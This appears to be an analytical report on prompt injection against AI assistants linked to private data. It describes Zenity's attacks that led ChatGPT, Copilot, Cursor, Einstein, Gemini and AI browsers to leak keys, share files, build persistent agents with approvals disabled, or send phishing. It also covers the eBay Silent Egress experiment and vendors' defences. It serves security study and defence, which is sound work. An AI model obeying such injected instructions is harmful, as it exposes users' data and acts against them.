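Lockdown Mode treats connected data differently depending on the account. In June, according to Help Net Security, personal users in this mode could still search data that ChatGPT had copied from a connected service in advance, but could not access the service live or change anything in it. On its current help page, OpenAI says only that the mode blocks live access and changes "when those actions conflict with its security protections", so personal users cannot tell from the page whether ChatGPT may still search their Drive.

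In managed workspaces, administrators decide which apps, and which actions within them, remain available in Lockdown Mode. OpenAI advises them against allowing any app they don't trust, and against letting ChatGPT make changes in a trusted app if an outsider might see the result. It considers reading from a trusted app less risky because reading changes nothing, but notes that the app can still supply the sensitive data that an attacker wants.

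Administrators need to consider ChatGPT's read and write access to Google Drive together. If ChatGPT can read Drive, hidden instructions may still lead it to the keys. If it can also edit or share files, it could put the keys in a document that the attacker can open, without needing an image or web address.

OpenAI does not guarantee that Lockdown Mode prevents leaks, and Check Point soon found a way around it. TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* reported in November 2026 that the weakness was in ChatGPT's previews of web pages written in code. OpenAI had blocked these previews from contacting outside servers without the user's approval, but a pop-up window opened in a certain way bypassed the restrictions. In the worst case, the window could open without a click. OpenAI has since fixed the flaw.

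Most ChatGPT users will never turn on Lockdown Mode, and OpenAI does not think they need to. Its security chief, Dane Stuckey, said it was "not meant for everyone" and that the loss of features was worthwhile for people at elevated risk. Willison (2026) concluded that ChatGPT's default settings do not give robust protection against a sufficiently determined attacker. That seems fair, since leaving Lockdown Mode off keeps open the routes that OpenAI closes for the customers most at risk.

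OpenAI gives a similar warning through its Elevated Risk labels, which it introduced on the same day as Lockdown Mode. The labels appear beside certain network-connected features of ChatGPT, Atlas and Codex, such as the option to give Codex internet access, and warn of risks that the industry has not yet fully addressed. They don't block anything, but according to OpenAI's *Elevated Risk labels*, the company offers labelled features outside its standard warranties. OpenAI plans to remove each label once it judges the feature safe enough for general use.

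## Why assistants connected to private data stay exposed

OpenAI's repairs mostly closed the routes by which data could leave ChatGPT. They did not change the conditions that made the leak possible, which many other assistants share. Seven weeks before Zenity's talk, Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, gave those conditions a name. An attacker can easily steal data, he warned, through an assistant that has three abilities:

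- it reads text that strangers can write;
- it can reach the user's private data;
- it can send information to the outside world.

When an assistant can read strangers' documents, search private files and send data out, any text that an attacker gets in front of the model can direct it to find private data and send it out. The attacker would have nothing to steal if the assistant couldn't open private data, and no way to direct the search if it never read a stranger's text. In Zenity's demonstration, the document contained the attacker's text, and ChatGPT used the Connector to reach the private data and an image to send it out.

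A single tool can supply all three abilities. Willison's example is a tool that links assistants to GitHub, the code-sharing site. It can read what strangers post on a user's public projects, read the user's private code, and publish changes that strangers can see.

OpenAI gave a similar account in March 2026, but with two parts. It says an attacker needs a source, which is a way to influence the assistant, and a sink, which is a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context. Sinks can include sending data to a third party, following a link or using a tool. This account therefore also covers attacks that steal nothing, such as one that makes an assistant buy something or change a record.

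Most of the defences OpenAI added to ChatGPT, including the public-address rule and Lockdown Mode, restrict its ability to send data out. Disconnecting Google Drive removes its access to the private data stored there. Refusing files from outsiders reduces how much text from strangers it reads, but such text can still arrive in an email or a shared file. Training removes none of these three abilities and only makes the model less likely to follow instructions in what it reads.

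### Soft and hard boundaries

Training is what Bargury calls a soft boundary. In Zenity Labs' *Why Aren’t We Making Any Progress In Security From AI*, he contrasts soft boundaries with hard boundaries, which are limits in ordinary software that make an action impossible whatever the model outputs.

Soft boundaries can work anywhere, but Bargury says a bypass "isn't a bug" because a statistical system is bound to make some mistakes. Hard boundaries work best within one company's products, where the developers know every path the data can take. They fail through software bugs, which developers can find and fix. *When Guardrails Arent Enough* (Brauchler, 2025), the slides for another Black Hat talk that year, also describes guardrails as statistical measures without "hard" guarantees.

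Bargury gave three examples of hard boundaries in AI products. Microsoft Copilot did not display Markdown images, Salesforce Einstein showed customer records without having a model read them, and ChatGPT checked image addresses with url_safe. He added that each would hold until someone found a bypass. About three weeks later, his own team showed ways to bypass the Salesforce and OpenAI boundaries.

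A hard boundary can therefore still fail if its rules leave a gap. Anthropic had a strict rule that Claude's web-reading tool could open only addresses that the user had typed or a search had returned. Willison, in *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, describes how Ayush Paul found an exception in July 2026. The tool could also follow links on pages it had already opened, so a malicious site could offer a link for each letter and have Claude spell out the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic removed the exception. With a soft boundary, it would have had to anticipate every wording of the attack.

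### The other AgentFlayer targets

Zenity attacked five other products in the same project. *Pwn the Enterprise* reports the outcomes and most of the vendors' answers, and SecurityWeek reports later statements from Salesforce and Google.

| Target | What Zenity made the assistant do | The vendor's answer |
|---|---|---|
| Microsoft Copilot Studio | Email out a company's customer database | Blocked the prompts Zenity had used and paid a bounty |
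| Cursor with Jira | Collect a developer's secret keys and send them out | Called it a known issue and advised users to review the tools they connect |
| Salesforce Einstein | Replace customers' email addresses so that their mail passed through the attacker's server | Closed the report, saying engineers were working on a fix; later said it had fixed the flaw on 11 July 2025 |
| Google Gemini | Show a phishing link, or give the attacker's bank details as a supplier's | Closed the report; later said new layered defences fixed this type of issue |
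| Microsoft 365 Copilot | Show a phishing link when asked to summarise emails | Closed the report |

Zenity told SecurityWeek that the vendors had marked the last four as "won't fix". That was too harsh on Salesforce, which promised a fix without giving a date, according to the reply Bargury himself quotes. Google's statement is harder to assess because it does not specify which defence stopped Zenity's attack.

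The Copilot Studio attack exploited a missing hard boundary. Sharbat said in *Sloppy AI defenses take cybersecurity back to the 1990s, researchers say* that such agents often filter inputs and outputs but have "no filter between the LLM and its tools". Microsoft blocked Zenity's prompts, but the agent kept the same access to the database. The Cursor attack assumed that the developer had turned a boundary off by enabling a mode in which Cursor acts without asking for approval at each step.

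Once Einstein had changed the addresses, the company's own staff would send their messages to the attacker, so Einstein did not need to send any data out itself. A check on images or links would not have helped, but requiring approval for changes to many contact records might have.

The distinction is less useful for Gemini and Microsoft 365 Copilot, where the harm comes from users acting on what the assistant tells them. Blocking images in Copilot does not stop it from giving users a wrong bank account number. A vendor could exclude strangers' emails from summaries, but then the assistant could no longer summarise an inbox.

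### The Silent Egress experiment

Four researchers at eBay compared the two kinds of defence directly. Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026), in *Silent Egress*, built an assistant that could make web requests and ran it on a small open model, Qwen 2.5 with 7 billion parameters. They put a secret in the text the model was working from, then asked it to summarise a web page containing hidden instructions to send the secret to their server. ("Egress" is the technical term for outgoing network traffic.)

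The researchers put the instructions in one of four parts of the page, had the assistant reach the page directly or through redirects, and asked for the secret whole or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times. The assistant contacted their server in 423 of the 480 runs (88%), and in 95% of those its reply to the user looked harmless. It never contacted the server in 120 runs with ordinary pages.

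Asking for the secret in pieces lowered the attack's success rate from 99% to 77%. This supports the idea that attackers fail more often when they have to extract a secret piece by piece, though 77% is still high.

The researchers then added defences to the setup in which the attack had worked every time, again with 30 runs for each:

| Defence | Model tried to send data | Data left |
|---|---|---|
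| None | 100% | 100% |
| Warning in the system instructions | 67% | 67% |
| Tags marking the page as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Warning and tags together | 57% | 57% |
| List of approved domains | 100% | 0% |
| Block on suspicious addresses | 83% | 0% |

The zero for approved domains was almost guaranteed by the design, because the researchers chose an attacker's domain that was not on the list. The 100% beside it is more informative. The model followed the attacker's instructions every time and still leaked nothing, so the protection did not depend on the model refusing them.

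A real attacker would look for an approved domain that accepts data from anyone, as Zenity did with the cloud storage service. The researchers acknowledge that compromised sites and redirects can defeat lists of approved domains. Willison describes a January 2026 case in which Claude Cowork, Anthropic's assistant for office work, could contact only approved domains, including Anthropic's own service. The security firm PromptArmor had the assistant upload the user's files to an attacker's account on that service.

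Two other filters in the study, which looked for words such as "password" or for random-looking strings, also stopped every leak. Those results deserve less weight because the model tried to send data in only 23% and 0% of runs with the filters on, and a filter on outgoing requests shouldn't affect how often a model attempts one. The researchers suggest that the model avoids random-looking strings when such monitoring is active, but they don't explain how it would detect the monitoring.

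The researchers acknowledge that the experiment also favoured the attacker, because the secret was in plain view and the system instructions were minimal. They suspect that stronger models could be more vulnerable because such models follow instructions better, but they tested only one model.

### The price of cutting access

Hard boundaries make assistants less useful. Bargury compares them to a surgeon removing a whole organ out of caution, and says vendors competing for customers have removed several of them. Anthropic, for example, was at first reluctant to let Claude browse the web. Willison noted in June 2025 that vendors had promptly fixed almost all the leaks he had collected, usually by blocking the assistant's ability to send data out. He considers this the easiest ability to restrict without making an assistant much less useful. But a vendor can't restrict it for users who combine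 tools from different companies themselves.

Users may approve dangerous actions even when an assistant asks before each risky step, a safeguard meant to preserve the assistant's abilities while keeping a person in control. Anthropic tested this with 1,053 paid software developers, replacing one permission request in each session with a clearly dangerous command. According to Willison, only 13.6% refused it. Anthropic published the figure to promote an automatic mode that would have blocked 89% of such commands, so it had an interest in the comparison. The result still casts doubt on any safeguard that relies on a confirmation box, including OpenAI's.

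Lan and colleagues propose tracking where information comes from. The system would label text from the web as untrusted, along with anything the model produced under its influence, and labelled requests would be checked before being sent. But nobody can tell which parts of a model's output a document influenced, so to be safe the system would have to treat everything after the first untrusted document as suspect. An assistant that had just summarised a supplier's contract might be unable to search the user's Drive in the same conversation.

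An easier precaution is to make the data less valuable to a thief. Willison recommends giving coding assistants keys only for test accounts with strict spending limits.

### How often models refuse

OpenAI's main response is that most of the attacks it knows of fail because ChatGPT refuses. Evidence from other companies' models supports the general point. *What happened after 2,000 people tried to hack my AI assistant* (Irarrázaval, 2026) describes a public challenge to email an assistant running on Claude Opus 4.6 and make it reveal a file of secrets. More than 2,000 people sent over 6,000 emails, some posing as administrators or inventing emergencies, but the assistant never leaked the secrets. Irarrázaval was less worried about prompt injection afterward.

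The assistant had some advantages that a ChatGPT user's would not. Its instructions named the file it had to protect and told it not to reply to emails. After about 500 messages, it wrote in its memory that it was probably part of a security exercise. Obvious attacks also led it to treat later emails in the same batch as suspicious, until Irarrázaval changed the setup to process each email separately. Zenity's document, by contrast, reached an assistant whose task was to help its user find things in Google Drive.

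Anthropic commissioned a more systematic test from Trajectory Labs, which tried 72 attack scenarios on Claude Code, Anthropic's coding assistant. None of 720 attempts succeeded against three recent models in automatic mode. Willison wanted more independent confirmation, and he doubted that this mode could catch a malicious software package that the assistant installs as an apparently normal part of running a project's tests.

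Attackers can also try the same attack on many people. If a hidden instruction works once in 100 attempts, and each attempt is independent, an attacker who tries it on 100 people has a 63% chance of at least one success (1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰). With 500 people, the chance is over 99%. For this reason, Willison calls 99% a failing grade in security, although that success rate would be excellent for most other software.

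Better filters may not solve the problem. OpenAI reports that the most effective attacks now resemble social engineering, the deception that fraudsters use on people. A filter would have to recognise a plausible lie, often without the context needed to check it. OpenAI therefore compares an assistant to a customer-service employee who can issue refunds. The employer expects some customers to fool the employee, so it limits how much the employee can refund.

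### Attacks outside the laboratory

Google said in August 2025 that prompt injection was rarely seen in real attacks, but it was also defending its own product. Its later scan of public web pages partly supported the claim, and many of the injections it found were pranks, experiments or attempts to improve a site's ranking. However, malicious injections increased by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026. Google gave no total, so the increase could have been from a very low level. It expected attacks to become more common and more sophisticated.

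By July there was clearer evidence of criminal use. Mascellino (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents*, reported that the security company Zscaler had found two real campaigns. One used a fake software documentation page to tell coding assistants they had to buy a $3 licence key with cryptocurrency. Zscaler tried the page on 26 models in its own test assistant, and four made the payment. The other campaign told assistants that a copy of a cryptocurrency site was genuine.

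In October the security company Barracuda described a phishing email with hidden instructions that could make an assistant present the email as legitimate or urgent. In *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails*, Mascellino (2026) notes that Barracuda did not say how widespread the campaign was. Another security company, Proofpoint, found injection tools for sale on closed forums from about $150 a month, according to SecurityBrief UK, but said attackers still relied heavily on methods that target people, because those methods still work.

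In the most recent case, Alibaba Cloud admitted on 2 December 2026 that its service had sent AI agents instructions to hand over information about the user's computer. The Hacker News' *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (2026) reports that a developer received these instructions from the company's official command-line tool in place of ordinary answers. The instructions asked for the user's login name, the email address attached to their code and the agent's own instructions, among other things. Alibaba Cloud called this a measure against automated abuse and said it would stop. The developer sent nothing, and there is no evidence that any agent complied. Still, the case means that an assistant also has to distrust replies from a supplier the user has chosen.

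Google's remark therefore no longer describes attempted attacks accurately. However, none of these reports identifies anyone whose assistant gave away private files, and the campaigns mostly aimed at payments, rankings and clicks. Such leaks could have gone unnoticed, since almost all the leaks in the eBay experiment left no trace in the reply to the user.

### Assistants that can act

The image in Zenity's 2025 attack could leak an API key but not a long document, and the attacker lost control once ChatGPT finished its reply. Neither limit applies once an assistant can change settings, share files or start other agents.

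In July 2026 Zenity disclosed AgentForger, a flaw in the part of ChatGPT where organisations build their own agents. An attacker could put instructions into a link to ChatGPT. When an employee clicked the link, ChatGPT built a new agent, connected it to the apps the employee had already authorised, turned off its approval requests and scheduled it to fetch more instructions from the attacker. The agent could keep reading email and files, and writing to colleagues in the employee's name, long after the click.

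The approval requests offered no protection because the process that built the agent could also disable them. Zenity reported the flaw, an ordinary software bug, on 4 June, and OpenAI fixed it within four days by removing the part of the link that carried the instructions.

Zenity's next findings will be harder to fix. At Black Hat in August 2026, it presented attacks on five AI browsers and browser assistants, which can read pages and click on them for the user. A normal browser prevents one website from reading or controlling another where the user is logged in, but a browser assistant works across all of them, so a comment on one site can lead it to act on another.

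SecurityWeek reports that a comment on X led ChatGPT Atlas, OpenAI's browser, to open WhatsApp and send phishing messages to all the victim's contacts. It also reports that a malicious email could make Claude in Chrome copy the victim's inbox to the attacker and share every file in the victim's Google Drive. Sharing the files avoids the size limit of the 2025 attack, because the attacker can open whole documents on Google's website. Checking image addresses would not prevent this sharing.

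Zenity reported one problem to Anthropic, which classified the report as "informative", and another to OpenAI, which acknowledged it. SecurityWeek reported in August that both problems remained unpatched more than six months later. CTech's *Israeli researchers uncover zero-click attacks targeting AI browsers* says some of the five vendors issued fixes and others described the behaviour as intended. Perplexity blocked its browser's access to files on the user's computer, but Zenity got around the fix twice, according to Notebookcheck.

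Bargury told CTech that "this is not a bug we can patch away". He is right that these browsers are meant to read one site and act on another. Vendors can still restrict particular actions, but only if they block every way of performing them. Atlas could not press Amazon's final purchase button, so in Zenity's demonstration it filled the basket, changed the delivery address to the attacker's and asked Rufus, Amazon's AI assistant, to place the order.
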